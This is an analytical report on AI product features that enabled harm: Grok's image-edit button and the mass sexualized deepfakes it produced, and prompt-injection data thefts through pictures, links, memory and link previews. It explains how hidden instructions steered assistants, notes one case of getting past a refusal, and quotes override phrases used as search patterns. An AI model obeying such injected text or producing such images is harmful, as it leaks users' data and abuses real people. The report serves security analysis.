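People could already edit strangers' pictures in other ways. X's mobile app had offered the feature before the website did, according to Roboin's *X (Twitter) adds a button to edit other people’s images with Grok* (2025), but users had to press and hold a picture to find it. People could also reply to a post, tag Grok's public account and ask for a change. And as 80 Level's *Twitter/X Now Lets Anyone AI-Edit Your Images, And There's No Opting Out* points out, anyone could download a picture and alter it with another program.

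*@Grok Put Her in a Bunny Suit* (Fontana, Rahimzadeh and Zannettou, 2026) explains how Grok's integration with X made it easier to create and publish fake sexual images of real people. An abuser used to need a suitable program, a photograph of the person, a private place to make the image and somewhere to publish it. On X, the photograph and the program were already in the same place, and a request to Grok's account produced a public post, so the abuser no longer had to decide separately to publish.

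On December 31, Musk shared a Grok-generated picture of himself in a bikini. Grok then received many requests to put women and children in bikinis or remove their clothes. The women included celebrities and ordinary users. Fatimah (2026), in *Grok under fire for sexualizing women and children's images*, quotes an admission of "lapses in safeguards" posted by Grok's account. But a chatbot's post is weak evidence of what its maker knew, and X and xAI didn't answer questions from the New York Times.

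### How researchers counted the images

The Center for Countering Digital Hate (CCDH), a nonprofit that studies online abuse, estimated that Grok produced about 3 million sexualized images on X between December 29 and January 8. It took a random sample of 20,000 from the 4.6 million images Grok made in that time. An AI model, OpenAI's GPT-4.1-mini, classed 12,995 of the sampled images, or 65%, as sexualized, and CCDH applied that share to the total, according to The Decoder's *Elon Musk's AI chatbot Grok flooded X with millions of sexualized images*.

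The sample is large enough that the 3 million figure depends much less on chance than on what CCDH counted. It included any picture of a person in a sexual position, in revealing clothing such as underwear or swimwear, or covered in fluid meant to look sexual. CCDH judged the finished picture, so the total can include people who asked for a bikini picture of themselves. According to Red Hot Cyber, the classifier scored 95% on a standard measure of accuracy.

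CCDH also found 101 sexualized images of children in the sample, each checked by hand, which gives an estimate of more than 23,000 overall. With only 101 examples, chance alone could put the true figure between about 19,000 and 28,000. In *Grok is a Make-or-Break Test for the EU’s Digital Services Act*, Vergnolle (2026) treats the estimate as a minimum, writing of "at least" 23,000 images of child sexual abuse, and assumes that every image in CCDH's broader category meets the legal definition.

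A separate count for the New York Times supports the general scale. Conger, Freedman and Thompson (2026), in *Elon Musk’s Grok A.I. Chatbot Made Millions of Sexualized Images*, used one model to detect women and another to detect sexual content in 525,000 of Grok's images, then checked a selection by hand. They estimated conservatively that 41% of Grok's posts, or 1.8 million in nine days, were sexualized images of women. For comparison, one of the largest forums for fake sexual videos of real people hosted 43,000 videos at its peak in 2023.

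### The button or the model

The table combines the counts by Conger and colleagues with the later measurement by Fontana and colleagues.

| Period | What had changed on X | What the researchers found |
|---|---|---|
| December 22 to 30, 2025 | Edit button arrived partway through | 311,762 images from Grok's account |
| December 31 to January 8 | Musk's bikini picture | More than 4.4 million images |
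| From January 8 or 9 | Payment required for images from Grok's account | Significantly fewer images, no exact count |
| From mid-January | No images of real people in revealing clothing from Grok's account | Most bikini requests ignored, leotards and one-piece swimsuits still produced |
| February 19 to March 27 | Same restrictions | Sexual images without likely consent in about 3% of image conversations |

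The number of images rose about 14-fold after Musk's post, but the button had already been available for several days. So the button alone doesn't explain the increase, and Musk's promotion of this particular use may have mattered more.

These counts also don't measure how often people used the button, because they cover images that Grok's account posted, many of them for people who had tagged Grok in a reply. Bloomberg's *XAI Limits Grok Images After Uproar Over Sexualized Content* (2026) reported on January 9 that Grok had begun telling X users they needed a subscription to make or edit images. But *Elon Musk’s X Partially Restricts Grok’s Image Editing Amid Deepfake Controversy* summarizes tests by The Verge, which found that the edit button and the press-and-hold menu still worked on free accounts. The count dropped sharply after this first restriction, even though the button remained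 free. Either most of the counted images had come through the public account, or people moved to the button and made images that nobody was counting.

With the second restriction, X kept the public account but made Grok ignore most requests for bikinis. X could therefore limit the harm without removing the feature, and it did so within about three weeks of launch. The restriction didn't cover Grok's own app and website, which still made sexual images in private.

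The rule was also narrow. Only 5.2% of the abusive conversations that Fontana and colleagues found in February and March included a specific request for swimwear, while 54.1% included a request for some kind of sexualized outfit, such as a bikini, bunny suit, maid costume or latex. Users may have switched to clothes that the rule didn't name, though nobody measured the same categories in early January.

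The fall from 65% to 3% probably reflects a large improvement, but the two percentages measure different things. CCDH judged finished pictures, while Fontana and colleagues counted only conversations in which a user explicitly asked for a sexual image of a real person and Grok complied. A model flagged 2,643 of about 50,000 conversations, and a human reviewer confirmed 1,526. In 57 of these, users presented themselves as the person in the picture, so they may have consented.

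A fifth of the confirmed cases came from nine accounts, so X could have reduced the abuse in this sample by suspending them, at least until their owners opened new ones.

If the model had refused to make these images, the button would have been a harmless way to change a background. The harm didn't require the button, because users had other ways to make the same request. X increased the scale of the harm by putting the model next to hundreds of millions of photographs and automatically publishing the results from a public account. The evidence is too limited to put a percentage on the button's share of the harm, but removing the button alone would probably have prevented only a modest part of it.

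### Why injection defenses had nothing to catch

The ChatGPT users clicked Share themselves, and the X users typed their own requests, so there was no outsider's text for a prompt injection filter to catch. Even a model that could perfectly separate its user's words from everyone else's would have behaved the same way.

ChatGPT's model had already finished its answers when the user ticked the box, and ordinary web software then published the page. Blocking outside images or checking the addresses that ChatGPT opens would have made no difference, because the data left through a page that OpenAI hosted.

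With Grok, the photographs were already public, so removing one part of the lethal trifecta would not have protected the people in them.

A filter for sexual content could have helped on X. However, Fontana and colleagues found that users often asked for several small changes, such as an open button, wet fabric or a new pose. Each might look innocent alone, so the filter would have to compare the result with the original photograph and take earlier edits into account. It would be simpler to let only the person who posted a picture edit it, though others could still upload a copy and edit that.

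In April 2026, X put Grok's editing tools into the window where users write their own posts. Engadget's *X has a slightly more functional photo editor now* contrasts this with the earlier "freewheeling approach", in which any user could reply to a post and ask Grok for an edit.

### Lawsuits and investigations

X first held users responsible. TechSpot reported that an X spokesperson said anyone who prompted Grok to make illegal content would face the same consequences as someone who uploaded it. In the United States, Section 230 of the Communications Decency Act generally protects platforms from liability for what their users post. Critics argue that this protection shouldn't apply here because the platform's own AI makes the picture.

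Both positions are now before the courts. In July 2026, xAI sued a South Carolina man, alleging that he had used Grok to make child sexual abuse material. It was the company's first lawsuit against a user, according to Stanciuc's *xAI’s first lawsuit against a user tests who is responsible* (2026). On November 23, two state attorneys general sued Musk's companies, arguing that the companies avoided safeguards when designing and launching Grok, according to AsiaOne's *States sue Musk companies over flood of sexualised images* (2026).

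Critics had called the paid-only limit "insulting" and "not effective", according to Nolan's *Lawmakers and victims criticize the choice to limit Grok’s AI image generation* (2026). In June, despite X's January promises, *Wired* still found dozens of sexual deepfakes of celebrities and an American politician on Grok's website, along with public guides to getting around the restrictions, according to Clubic's *Malgré ses promesses, Grok continue d’héberger des deepfakes sexuels non consentis* (2026). SpaceX, xAI's parent company, put the legal risks connected with Grok at more than €460 million in a filing for its stock market launch.

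Authorities in France, India, Australia, Malaysia and Brazil, among others, looked into Grok. Ofcom, Britain's media regulator, opened an investigation in January and could fine X up to 10% of its worldwide revenue or £18 million, whichever is greater (Indonesia Tribune, *Ofcom Investigates Elon Musk's X Over Grok AI Sexual Deepfakes*, 2026).

The European Commission opened its own investigation under the Digital Services Act, which requires very large platforms to assess and reduce the risks of their services. Vergnolle examined X's three annual risk reports and found that none assessed Grok, although X had built it into the platform. One report rated the spread of child sexual abuse material as a "low risk item". Vergnolle argues that the law already required X to include Grok, and wants the Commission to stop platforms from choosing which integrated services to leave out. The Commission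 had not announced a decision by early December 2026.

### The EU ban on "nudification"

Since December 2, 2026, EU law has also banned AI systems that make realistic intimate or sexually explicit images of identifiable people without their explicit consent, and systems that make child sexual abuse material. The ban comes from *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026), which amends the AI Act.

The ban covers apps built for undressing people, but also general products whose design, training or "user-facing functionalities" make such images a foreseeable and repeatable result, if the company lacks adequate safeguards. A company has to consider foreseeable misuse and correct the misuse that people report. A regulator could therefore consider an edit button as well as the model behind it, and the company can't defend itself simply by showing that it meant the button for something else.

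Many of the Grok images would still fall outside the ban on intimate images of adults, because the regulation's introductory text excludes realistic, partly nude pictures that don't reveal intimate parts or show sexual activity. That exclusion would probably cover a typical bikini edit, so CCDH's 3 million is not an estimate of how many images the new law would have prohibited. Other laws may apply to the excluded images.

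Companies that break the ban risk fines of up to €35 million or 7% of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher. For small companies, the maximum is the lower of the two, according to Jarovsky's *New AI Act Ban Takes Effect Today* (2026). Enforcement has started slowly. In late November, 81 members of the European Parliament warned that Belgium, Austria and Croatia still lacked a proper framework for enforcing the ban, according to The Brussels Times' *EU ban on AI nudification tools takes effect* (2026). NewsIreland.EU's *EU bans AI ‘nudification’ but apps still online* (2026) reported on December 3 that people in the EU could still open nine of the ten most popular nudification websites.

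## What the cases have in common and where they differ

The table compares the eight cases. The eighth case has the last two rows because ChatGPT's share checkbox and Grok's image-edit button caused harm in different ways.

| Feature | Purpose | Source of the hostile input | How the harm got out | Did it depend on fooling the model? | Real harm or demonstration | What ended it |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
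| Repeating text on a public account (Tay, later Grok) | Entertain and answer users | Users, openly | Public posts, and in 2026 a wallet payment | No, though Grok had to decode a disguised order | Real | Microsoft withdrew Tay; Bankr blocked Grok's replies |
| Pictures in chat answers | Illustrate answers | Web pages, forms, emails | A picture's web address | Yes | Demonstrations | Blocked pictures, stricter address checks |
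| Microsoft 365 Copilot's search, links and saved files | Find and store work documents | Unopened emails, prepared links | Requests from Microsoft's own servers | Yes, except with a prefilled prompt | Demonstrations | Repairs on Microsoft's servers |
| Link previews | Show where a link leads | Documents, messages, web pages | The messaging app's request for the link | Yes | Demonstrations | No general fix; developers can turn previews off |
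| Memory | Spare users from repeating themselves | Web pages, files, emails, prefilled buttons | Later leaks or slanted answers | Yes, except with a prefilled prompt | Demonstrated leaks, real attempts at advertising | Repairs to single leaks; documents could still plant notes in 2026 |
| Claude's page reader and file uploads | Read pages, process files | Web pages, documents | A choice of links, uploads to a stranger's account | Yes | Demonstrations | Narrower rules for links and, in Cowork, for accounts |
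| Tool calls | Act in other services | Issue reports, guides, skill files | Pull requests, messages, web addresses | Yes | Demonstrations | Few confirmed fixes |
| ChatGPT's share checkbox | Help people find useful chats | Nobody | Search engine listings | No | Real | OpenAI removed the option |
| Grok's image-edit button | Edit pictures quickly | Users, openly | Pictures in public replies | No | Real | Limits on what Grok would draw, with partial success |

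### Old features, trusted domains and narrow repairs

Many of these features are older than chatbots. Websites had long loaded pictures from other sites and put search terms in their addresses, and messaging apps had link previews years before anyone connected an agent to them. A person normally chose the address in those products, but once a language model could write it, a stranger's text could determine where the request went and what it contained. Memory and tool calls are newer, but some attacks on them still relied on an older feature. For example, Copilot Cowork's message to its user leaked files only because Teams loaded the pictures in it.

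Several allow-lists included a domain that an attacker could use to extract data. Bing, Teams and GitHub's picture relay fetched outside addresses on request, so they could pass data to an attacker. Google Forms and Anthropic's upload service stored data where an attacker could collect it. Salesforce had let a permitted domain expire. Developers who use Claude's page reader can restrict it to domains they choose, which Willison considers a much stronger protection than the default rules. But the restriction works only if none of those domains can receive stolen data, and he calls finding domains that meet this condition "a tricky proposition".

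Vendors mostly blocked the route that a researcher had shown them. In June 2025, Willison listed 17 products and features that researchers had attacked to steal data since April 2023, from ChatGPT and Google Bard to Mistral's Le Chat and GitLab's Duo. Vendors had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the way data got out. That stops the reported theft, but the model will still follow another attacker's instructions if they reach it. For example, after OpenAI fixed ChatGPT's Mac app, web pages could still plant memories in ChatGPT.

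### Hidden instructions and features used as offered

With Tay, the share checkbox and the edit button, people used a feature as the company had offered it, and the harm was real. By contrast, nearly all the thefts by hidden instructions were demonstrations. The clearest exception is the payment from Grok's wallet in May 2026, a real loss even though most of the money was returned.

This doesn't show that hidden instructions are the smaller danger. Anyone could make Tay say something vile, and thousands of people saw the result, whereas a theft through a picture takes preparation and the victim may never notice. There may have been few such thefts, or few that anyone detected.

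The fixes that helped also differed. X reduced the abuse of people's photographs largely by changing what Grok would draw, while vendors responded to the data thefts mostly by changing the software around the model.

Prefilled prompts, as in SearchLeak and the "Summarize with AI" buttons, don't fit neatly into either group, because a stranger wrote the text but the product treated it as the user's own message.

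### Whether small features are the main attack surface

To show that convenience features are the main way AI products are attacked, someone would have to count attacks and sort them by the part of the product involved. There appears to be no such public count of cataloged vulnerabilities, bug-bounty reports or incidents. Willison's list comes closest, but he was collecting data thefts. Stolen data has to leave through a feature of some sort, so every attack on his list would involve one, however common other attacks were.

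Researchers also tend to look for flaws that are easy to prove, and a secret in a server log is clearer evidence than a slanted answer. Companies have reinforced this habit. OpenAI, for example, closed Rehberger's first report about planted memories as a model safety issue, and he then returned with a demonstration that stole data. Published reports therefore probably overstate the share of attacks that send data out.

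Studies of injection in real use have a different gap. They count hostile text on web pages and sort it by what the author wanted or how the author hid it. In April 2026, Google published the results of a search of Common Crawl, an archive that collects 2 to 3 billion web pages a month. Google looked for phrases such as "if you are an AI", had its Gemini model judge whether the text seemed out of place, and had people check the remainder. Most of the early matches were articles about prompt injection.

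The remaining pages contained pranks, attempts to promote a business, and instructions meant to keep AI systems away. One page sent AI readers to another that never finished loading. Google found only a few attempts to steal data, and these were crude. It saw no significant use of the exfiltration methods that researchers had published in 2025. The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google gives no absolute number, so the increase could represent few pages.

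Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, had published a more alarming account in March. It described 12 cases from live websites and concluded that attackers were using the technique. One page advertised "military glasses" at a fake discount and contained 24 attempts to make an AI reviewer approve the advertisement. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed case of such an attack working on a deployed reviewer.

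Of all the attempts Unit 42 detected, 28.6% were meant to make the AI system produce irrelevant output, such as a recipe. Another 14.2% were meant to destroy data and 6.2% to trigger a payment. Stealing information wasn't among the six most common aims. Unit 42 rates severity by intent, so a hidden comment telling agents to delete their database counts as critical even if no agent would obey it. This explains much of the difference in tone between Unit 42 and Google, which considered the destructive commands it found unlikely to succeed.

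Unit 42 writes that these attacks exploit harmless features such as page summaries. But summarizing a page is how the hostile text reaches the assistant, and for many assistants it is a main capability rather than a small extra.

Other studies also concentrate on the web. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) examines the prevalence, techniques and aims of injected instructions on web pages. According to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*, the security company Forcepoint searched public websites for patterns such as "Ignore previous instructions". A search for stock phrases would have missed EchoLeak's email, and searches of public pages don't cover the mailboxes, support tickets and uploaded files where many of the demonstrated attacks began.

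Microsoft's study of "Summarize with AI" buttons provides the best count of attacks through a single convenience feature in real use, though it too covers only attempts.

When researchers have used hidden instructions to steal data from an AI assistant, the data has often left through a minor feature that few people would have thought of as a way to send anything. But nobody has shown that such features account for most attacks on AI products, and most of the injected text found on the public web seems to be meant for something other than stealing data.

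### Where the fault lies

Willison traces the thefts to the model's failure to separate instructions from data, which Unit 42 also considers a key cause. That would explain why much the same attack worked on 17 products and features, many of them from different companies. It also means each new feature can give attackers another way to get data out. Willison (2025) quotes the security expert Bruce Schneier as writing that "we have zero agentic AI systems that are secure against these attacks."

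AI companies don't promise a complete fix soon. Anthropic's *Mitigating the risk of prompt injections in browser use*, written for the release of Claude Opus 4.5, calls injection "far from a solved problem". Gavish (2026) writes in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that it isn't the kind of problem a company solves and moves on from.

The case for fixing the feature starts from the same weakness. If nobody can remove that weakness, a company has to protect its product another way, and a fixed rule at least gives the same answer every time.

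Willison argued this point against The Economist in September 2025. The magazine had suggested that AI developers learn from Victorian engineers, who couldn't trust the quality of their iron and so built everything stronger than necessary. Willison largely agreed with this approach for building software on language models, but thought it unsuitable for security. He argued that if 1% of attacks get through, an attacker will find that 1%. The load on a bridge, by contrast, isn't deliberately aimed at the weakest girder.

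However, a rule gives certainty only about the route it describes, as Paul's attack on Claude's page reader showed. Someone who fixes features one at a time also has to find every route by which data can leave before an attacker does, and blocking those routes doesn't prevent harm inside the account.

Willison agrees with both sides, since he blames the model and recommends removing the route by which data leaves. That seems the most sensible position on theft by hidden instructions. How a company labels the problem still matters, because the label can determine who handles a report. Anthropic initially closed Rehberger's report about file uploads as a model safety issue, but eventually fixed Cowork by changing the software around the model.

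### How well current models resist injection

Recent models are much harder to fool. The testing company Gray Swan tried strong attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 in late 2025. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, a single attempt succeeded 4.7% of the time, and the rate rose to 33.6% with ten attempts and 63% with 100. In September 2026, Anthropic published Gray Swan's results for Claude Fable 5.1 in the model's system card. The rates were 0.1% for one attempt, 0.7% for ten and 1.0% for 15. The two tests may not have used the same attacks, so the figures don't measure the improvement exactly.

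The newer test had 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks. Gray Swan chose the attacks because they had worked on several models. Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash did best among other companies' models, with an attack success rate of 9.2% after 15 attempts. Most of the rest were between 24% and 53%, so a product's exposure still depends heavily on which model its maker chose.

Low scores on a fixed set of attacks can be misleading. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reported that no attack on Claude Opus 5 had succeeded in 129 browser scenarios, and that its Gray Swan rate after 15 attempts was 2.0%. In the September system card, the same model's rate was 4.8%. By then, Anthropic had added nine scenarios and 670 attacks and changed some of the test conditions.

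Anthropic also tested Fable 5.1 with Shade, a Gray Swan program that learns to improve its attacks. Shade practiced on the test scenarios beforehand and had 200 attempts at each. For the browser tests, Anthropic instead reused attacks that testers had developed against an older Claude model. The table shows the share of attempts that succeeded. The safeguards include a check for injected instructions in tool results. In the browser tests, they also include auto mode's review of each action.

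| Test of Claude Fable 5.1 | Without injection safeguards | With safeguards |
|---|---|---|
| Coding, earlier version of Shade | 9.26% | 2.05% |
| Coding, stronger version of Shade | 56.87% | 12.80% |
| Operating a graphical screen | 0.07% | 0.07% |
| Browsing in Claude Cowork | 2.64% | 0% |

The February figures that VentureBeat reported for Claude Opus 4.6 showed no successful attacks in coding and many on a graphical screen. By September, the pattern had reversed. With 200 attempts at each of 14 screen scenarios, attacks succeeded in only two. In coding, the stronger Shade found a successful attack in 38 of 40 scenarios without safeguards and 36 with them. Opus 5, which is newer than Opus 4.6, was successfully attacked in all 40, with or without safeguards. The perfect coding score in February may have depended as much on the attacker as on the model.

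All the successful attacks in the stronger coding test came through Claude Opus 4.8, an older model that Anthropic uses when a safety filter detects a request that might involve hacking. It handled about 64% of the requests in the test. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack. Those requests may have been easier, since the filter had already removed the ones that looked most like hacking, but the safeguard against one kind of misuse had still made the product more vulnerable to another.

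Those 2,826 requests suggest that training can bring the failure rate very low, which is encouraging for anyone who blames the model. But customers use the whole product, including the older model behind it, which is an argument for fixing features instead. Anthropic considers the stronger Shade much more capable than a realistic attacker, who wouldn't know the exact setup and would risk detection with repeated attempts. That seems fair, but if even the 0.1% rate applied to an email that 10,000 assistants read, about ten would follow its instructions.

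Anthropic has since released Fable 5.2, and *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (Mowshowitz, 2026) notes that the model's system card also covers prompt injection. Further gains against prompt injection would make thefts like EchoLeak rarer, but they wouldn't have prevented SearchLeak or the accidental publication of ChatGPT conversations.

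## Why threat modeling misses such features

Microsoft publishes instructions for threat modeling, yet its Copilot leaked data through pictures, links and saved files. The companies appear not to have published a threat model for any of the features in these cases, so outsiders cannot check what reviewers asked before launch. The available evidence consists of official instructions, product documentation, and how the companies handled reports afterward.

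### How a standard exercise runs

Microsoft's *Perform secure design review and threat modeling* describes a meeting of at least two hours with engineers, testers, product owners and security specialists. They list what the product does and what it must protect, such as private files or customers' trust. They then work from a data-flow diagram of the people and services outside the product, the programs that process data and the places that store it, with arrows for data moving between them. Dashed red lines, called trust boundaries, mark where data passes between areas with different levels of trust, such as the public internet and a company's network. The product may have to check or block data that crosses a boundary.

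The group goes through the diagram with a checklist. Microsoft uses STRIDE, whose letters stand for six kinds of threat:

- Spoofing: pretending to be someone else
- Tampering: changing data without permission
- Repudiation: doing something and then denying it
- Information disclosure: leaking private data
- Denial of service: crashing or overloading the system
- Elevation of privilege: gaining powers the person shouldn't have

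For each part of the diagram, the group asks whether any of the six STRIDE threats could happen there. It writes down who could carry out each attack, what they would need and what damage they could do. Microsoft warns that STRIDE can miss important design flaws and is no substitute for thinking like an attacker.

The six STRIDE categories suit theft better than open misuse. A user who made Tay repeat a slur wasn't impersonating anyone or breaking into anything, and X had given everyone permission to use Grok's edit button. Microsoft also tells teams to ask what would happen if an attacker abused a feature. That question covers both cases, but a team that only works through the six categories could skip it.

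### An email assistant on the diagram

Suppose a team draws the diagram for an assistant that reads a user's email and displays pictures in its answers. A message from an outside sender arrives in the mailbox. The assistant's software gives the model this message along with the user's question. The model's answer goes to the chat window in the user's browser, which requests any pictures in the answer from web servers.

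The team draws one trust boundary where outside email enters the mailbox and another where the browser contacts the internet. Because the model runs on the company's own servers, the team marks its answers as trusted, as it would the output of other internal programs. This is reasonable for most programs, such as software that adds up invoices, which will produce a total whatever the sender writes in the comments. But a language model's answer can depend on any sentence in any email it reads, so a team that marks the answer as trusted may miss that an outside sender can influence it.

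| Data flow | What the team asks if it trusts the model's output | What it asks if it doesn't |
|---|---|---|
| Outside email to mailbox | Is it spam or a virus? | The same |
| Mailbox to model | Does the user have permission to read this email? | Could the sender's text also control the answer? |
| Model to chat window | Nothing, since both are inside the product | Could the answer contain a picture address that a stranger chose? |
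| Chat window to picture server | Could the picture harm the browser? | Could the address contain text from other emails? |

If the team labels the model as trusted, it has no obvious reason to consider information disclosure when the browser requests a picture. Otherwise, the team would draw another boundary between the model and the chat window, and by applying STRIDE there it would find the leak that EchoLeak later used.

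Bullwinkel, Minnich and colleagues (2025) recommend the more cautious assumption that a model given untrusted input will produce "arbitrary output", including any private information it has received. Their paper, *Lessons From Red Teaming 100 Generative AI Products*, comes from Microsoft's AI red team, which attacks the company's own products to find their weaknesses.

Specialists disagree about how much threat modeling has to change for AI. Shostack + Associates, a threat modeling firm, argues in a white paper that ordinary data-flow diagrams can already represent language models and connectors. The firm applies STRIDE to the whole system and adds a second checklist, PHANTOM-B, for threats specific to the model. Microsoft puts more emphasis on how AI systems differ from other software, and its AI guidance notes that many teams find these systems tend to fail "in the gaps between components".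 *ThreMoLIA* (2025), a proposal for a new threat modeling method, warns that ordinary security practice is likely to overlook or mishandle threats specific to language models.

The email example supports Shostack + Associates on the diagram, because the team can find the leak using the same boxes and arrows once it changes one label. But STRIDE has no step that would lead the team to change that label, so someone on the team has to know about prompt injection already.

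There is little direct evidence about how many reviewers have the risks of language models in mind. *From Chasing Ghosts to Missed Attacks* (2026) reports interviews with staff who monitor companies' systems for attacks. After participants had named their own concerns, the researchers showed them five risks of language models, such as invented information, because they thought security experts might not have these in mind. That was an expectation, not a measurement, and the participants monitored systems for attacks rather than approving new products.

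### Features reviewed one at a time

Microsoft advises teams to focus on the features they are building or directly connect to, and to divide the system into smaller parts if a two-hour meeting isn't enough. This keeps the meeting manageable, but teams can miss an attack that crosses several parts. SearchLeak, for example, combined three weaknesses, none sufficient alone, according to The Next Web.

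A group that reviewed only Copilot's search link might have noticed that a stranger could choose the prompt, but reasoned that only the employee would see the answer. A group that reviewed only Bing's image search would have seen a server doing its intended job of fetching pictures from addresses that users supply. Neither group's diagram would have shown an email leaving the company. Microsoft does tell reviewers that attackers chain vulnerabilities together, but once a team has divided the system for review, someone still has to examine how the parts work together.

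Reviewing every combination of features quickly becomes impractical. A product with 20 small features has 190 pairs and 1,140 groups of three. When different companies make the features, as with Grok and Bankrbot or OpenClaw and Telegram, each company may have only part of the diagram.

Reviewing features separately doesn't explain every case, though. Tay's repetition game was dangerous as soon as Microsoft connected it to a public account, and Google's default list of permitted sites for Antigravity included the request-logging service webhook.site. A reviewer could have found either problem by looking at one feature.

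### Old features and inherited code

Companies are supposed to repeat threat modeling when a product changes. Microsoft's *Evaluate application threats with threat modeling* lists new integrations and added features among the reasons for an update. Adding an assistant to a messaging app clearly qualifies, but the developers responsible for link previews may not have changed any code. To them, the preview works as it did before, even though a model can now write the links. This would also explain why picture loading and search links caused trouble, but it is a guess because the companies haven't said when they last reviewed these features.

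A team can also inherit flaws from another company's code, as Google did with Antigravity. Google based Antigravity on the coding program Windsurf after paying about $2.4 billion to license the code. Johann Rehberger had reported flaws in Windsurf in May 2025. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* describes how he found some of the same flaws in Antigravity a week after its release that November. These included data leaks through pictures and through a tool for reading web pages.

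Rehberger had published articles about the Windsurf flaws in August, so Google's reviewers could have learned about them there. He guesses that Antigravity's release caught Google's security team somewhat off guard. If so, a better checklist wouldn't have helped much unless the team had a chance to use it before launch.

### Tests of models and tests of products

AI companies publish much more about their models than about the products built on them. For *The 2025 AI Agent Index*, Staufer, Feng and colleagues (2026) looked for public information on 30 widely used agents, including ChatGPT, Claude Code and Microsoft Copilot Studio. For each agent, they checked eight subjects related to safety, such as outside testing and known incidents. Of the 240 entries, 135 were empty.

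Only four of the 30 agents had a system card for the agent itself: ChatGPT Agent, OpenAI Codex, Claude Code and Gemini 2.5 Computer Use. Twenty-five disclosed no results from internal safety tests. The gaps were largest for business agents, which often work with customer records, and smallest for chat products. *The AI Agent Index* (Casper, Bailey et al., 2025) had found the same imbalance a year earlier, with ample information about what agents could do and little about how developers managed the risks.

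Staufer and colleagues worked from public documents and corrections from the developers, so a company with an empty entry may still have done testing. They gave the companies four weeks to correct the entries, but only four companies sent substantive comments. Full documentation doesn't guarantee that anyone examined the small features, either. Claude Code was the only agent with information on all eight subjects, and Rehberger had got it to leak a key through a Slack link preview in 2025.

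Microsoft's red team is the best evidence that companies test more than models. By October 2024, it had run more than 80 operations covering over 100 products. Bullwinkel and colleagues warn that an attack that works on a model may fail against the finished product, and that testers who ignore ordinary components such as databases and input filters will probably miss important flaws. In one operation, the team used prompts in a less common language to discover the names of a product's internal functions. It then planted hidden instructions that made the model write a script to run those functions, and the script extracted private user data.

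The paper uses an email assistant as its example. A scammer sends a message with hidden instructions, and the assistant gives the user a malicious link that could leak data. Bullwinkel and colleagues published the paper in January 2025, the same month Aim Labs reported EchoLeak to Microsoft. So people at Microsoft understood the general attack and knew they had to test whole products. It is unclear whether they had tried the attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot's images and links.

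The red team also only identified risks, while the product teams were responsible for fixing them. A flaw could therefore survive because the red team never looked for it, a product team decided not to fix it, or the fix covered only one version of the attack. The paper doesn't give enough detail about individual products to tell which happens most often.

### How companies sort the reports they receive

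A feature flaw can also be missed when different people are responsible for a model's behavior and its security. Microsoft treats a prompt injection that lets an attacker steal another user's data as a security vulnerability and gives it a severity rating. It assesses hateful, sexual or misleading content separately, without a severity rating. This separation makes sense because people can agree more easily on whether data left an account than on how offensive an answer is. But a feature can turn a content problem into a security problem, as ChatGPT's memory did.

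Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT* describes Rehberger's first memory report, from 2024. He planted false memories through a Google document, an uploaded picture and a web page. ChatGPT at first refused to save anything from the web page, but Rehberger got around this by adding a request for an image to the page. He concluded from this that OpenAI was relying on the model's judgment instead of a fixed rule.

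OpenAI closed the report as a "Model Safety Issue" rather than a security vulnerability. Rehberger objected that strangers could add to or delete a user's stored data, which he thought had nothing to do with model safety. According to Futurism, OpenAI released its partial fix only after he demonstrated a data theft.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT* describes the company's trouble reaching the right people at OpenAI. On December 23, 2024, Tenable asked OpenAI for a security contact about another memory flaw and received an automatic reply. A week later, OpenAI asked for technical details of the "support ticket", and Tenable had to explain that it was reporting a security problem.

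xAI did treat its reports as security submissions, but gave them the lowest rating. Rehberger, in *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*, describes a picture leak in X's iPhone app in late 2024. xAI first said it couldn't reproduce the leak. When his original method stopped working, he found another and confirmed it with three volunteers. After weeks of questions, xAI closed all his reports as "Informational" and said the leak had no practical impact. Under xAI's bounty rules, an informational report earns nothing, while even a low-severity flaw pays at least $250.

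A day or two after Rehberger published his findings, xAI appeared to stop Grok from putting chat history and usernames in the first picture's address. Grok still loaded pictures from unknown servers, and a separate Grok app released in January 2025 had the same leak. In August 2026, the OECD's *Grok AI Vulnerability Enables Encrypted Data Exfiltration Attack* recorded a newer flaw that xAI hadn't patched. The security company Adversa AI had found that encrypted instructions on a web page made Grok leak names, locations and chat histories.

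Willison (2025) reports that Google's page for bug hunters listed data leaks and the running of harmful code through the browser agent as "known issues" in Antigravity. Researchers therefore couldn't claim a reward for reporting them, although Google said it was working on fixes. According to Embrace The Red, Google began documenting the issues publicly after researchers started sending reports.

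Google handled a later Antigravity flaw as an ordinary bug. Pillar Security found a way around the program's Secure Mode and reported it on January 6, 2026. Google patched it on February 28 and paid a reward, according to CyberScoop. Secure Mode was meant to give users a specific protection, so it may have been easier to show that the protection had failed. Google had already warned users that leaks like the original ones could happen.

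Microsoft labeled SearchLeak "Critical", although neither of the flaw's two severity scores matched that label well. One of them, 6.5, counts only as medium. Under Microsoft's guidelines for AI flaws, theft that needs a click is normally "Important", one level below "Critical". The company can, however, consider how easy an attack is.

In June 2026, The Hacker News reported a second score of 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database. The Next Web disputed this and wrote that both Microsoft and the database gave 6.5. The change history on cvefeed.io, an independent site that tracks software vulnerabilities, supports The Hacker News, showing Microsoft's score on June 4 and a second assessment on June 8. The only difference is that Microsoft counted the victim's click, while the later assessment included no action by the victim. Microsoft's score fits the attack better because Varonis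 needed someone to open the link.

The disagreement probably did no harm here, because Microsoft had already fixed the flaw when it published the first score. OpenAI's and xAI's labels mattered more, because each company used one to close a report while the flaw still worked. These decisions came after launch, so they are only indirect evidence that unclear responsibility also weakens reviews before launch.

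### How obvious the flaws were beforehand

The warning signs look clearer in accounts of these attacks than they did during review, because readers already know which feature to suspect and read only about the failures. The reviewers had to pick that feature out from everything else in the product, and many similar features have never caused any known trouble. A fairer test would be to give reviewers the original designs without telling them the outcome and see which features they flag.

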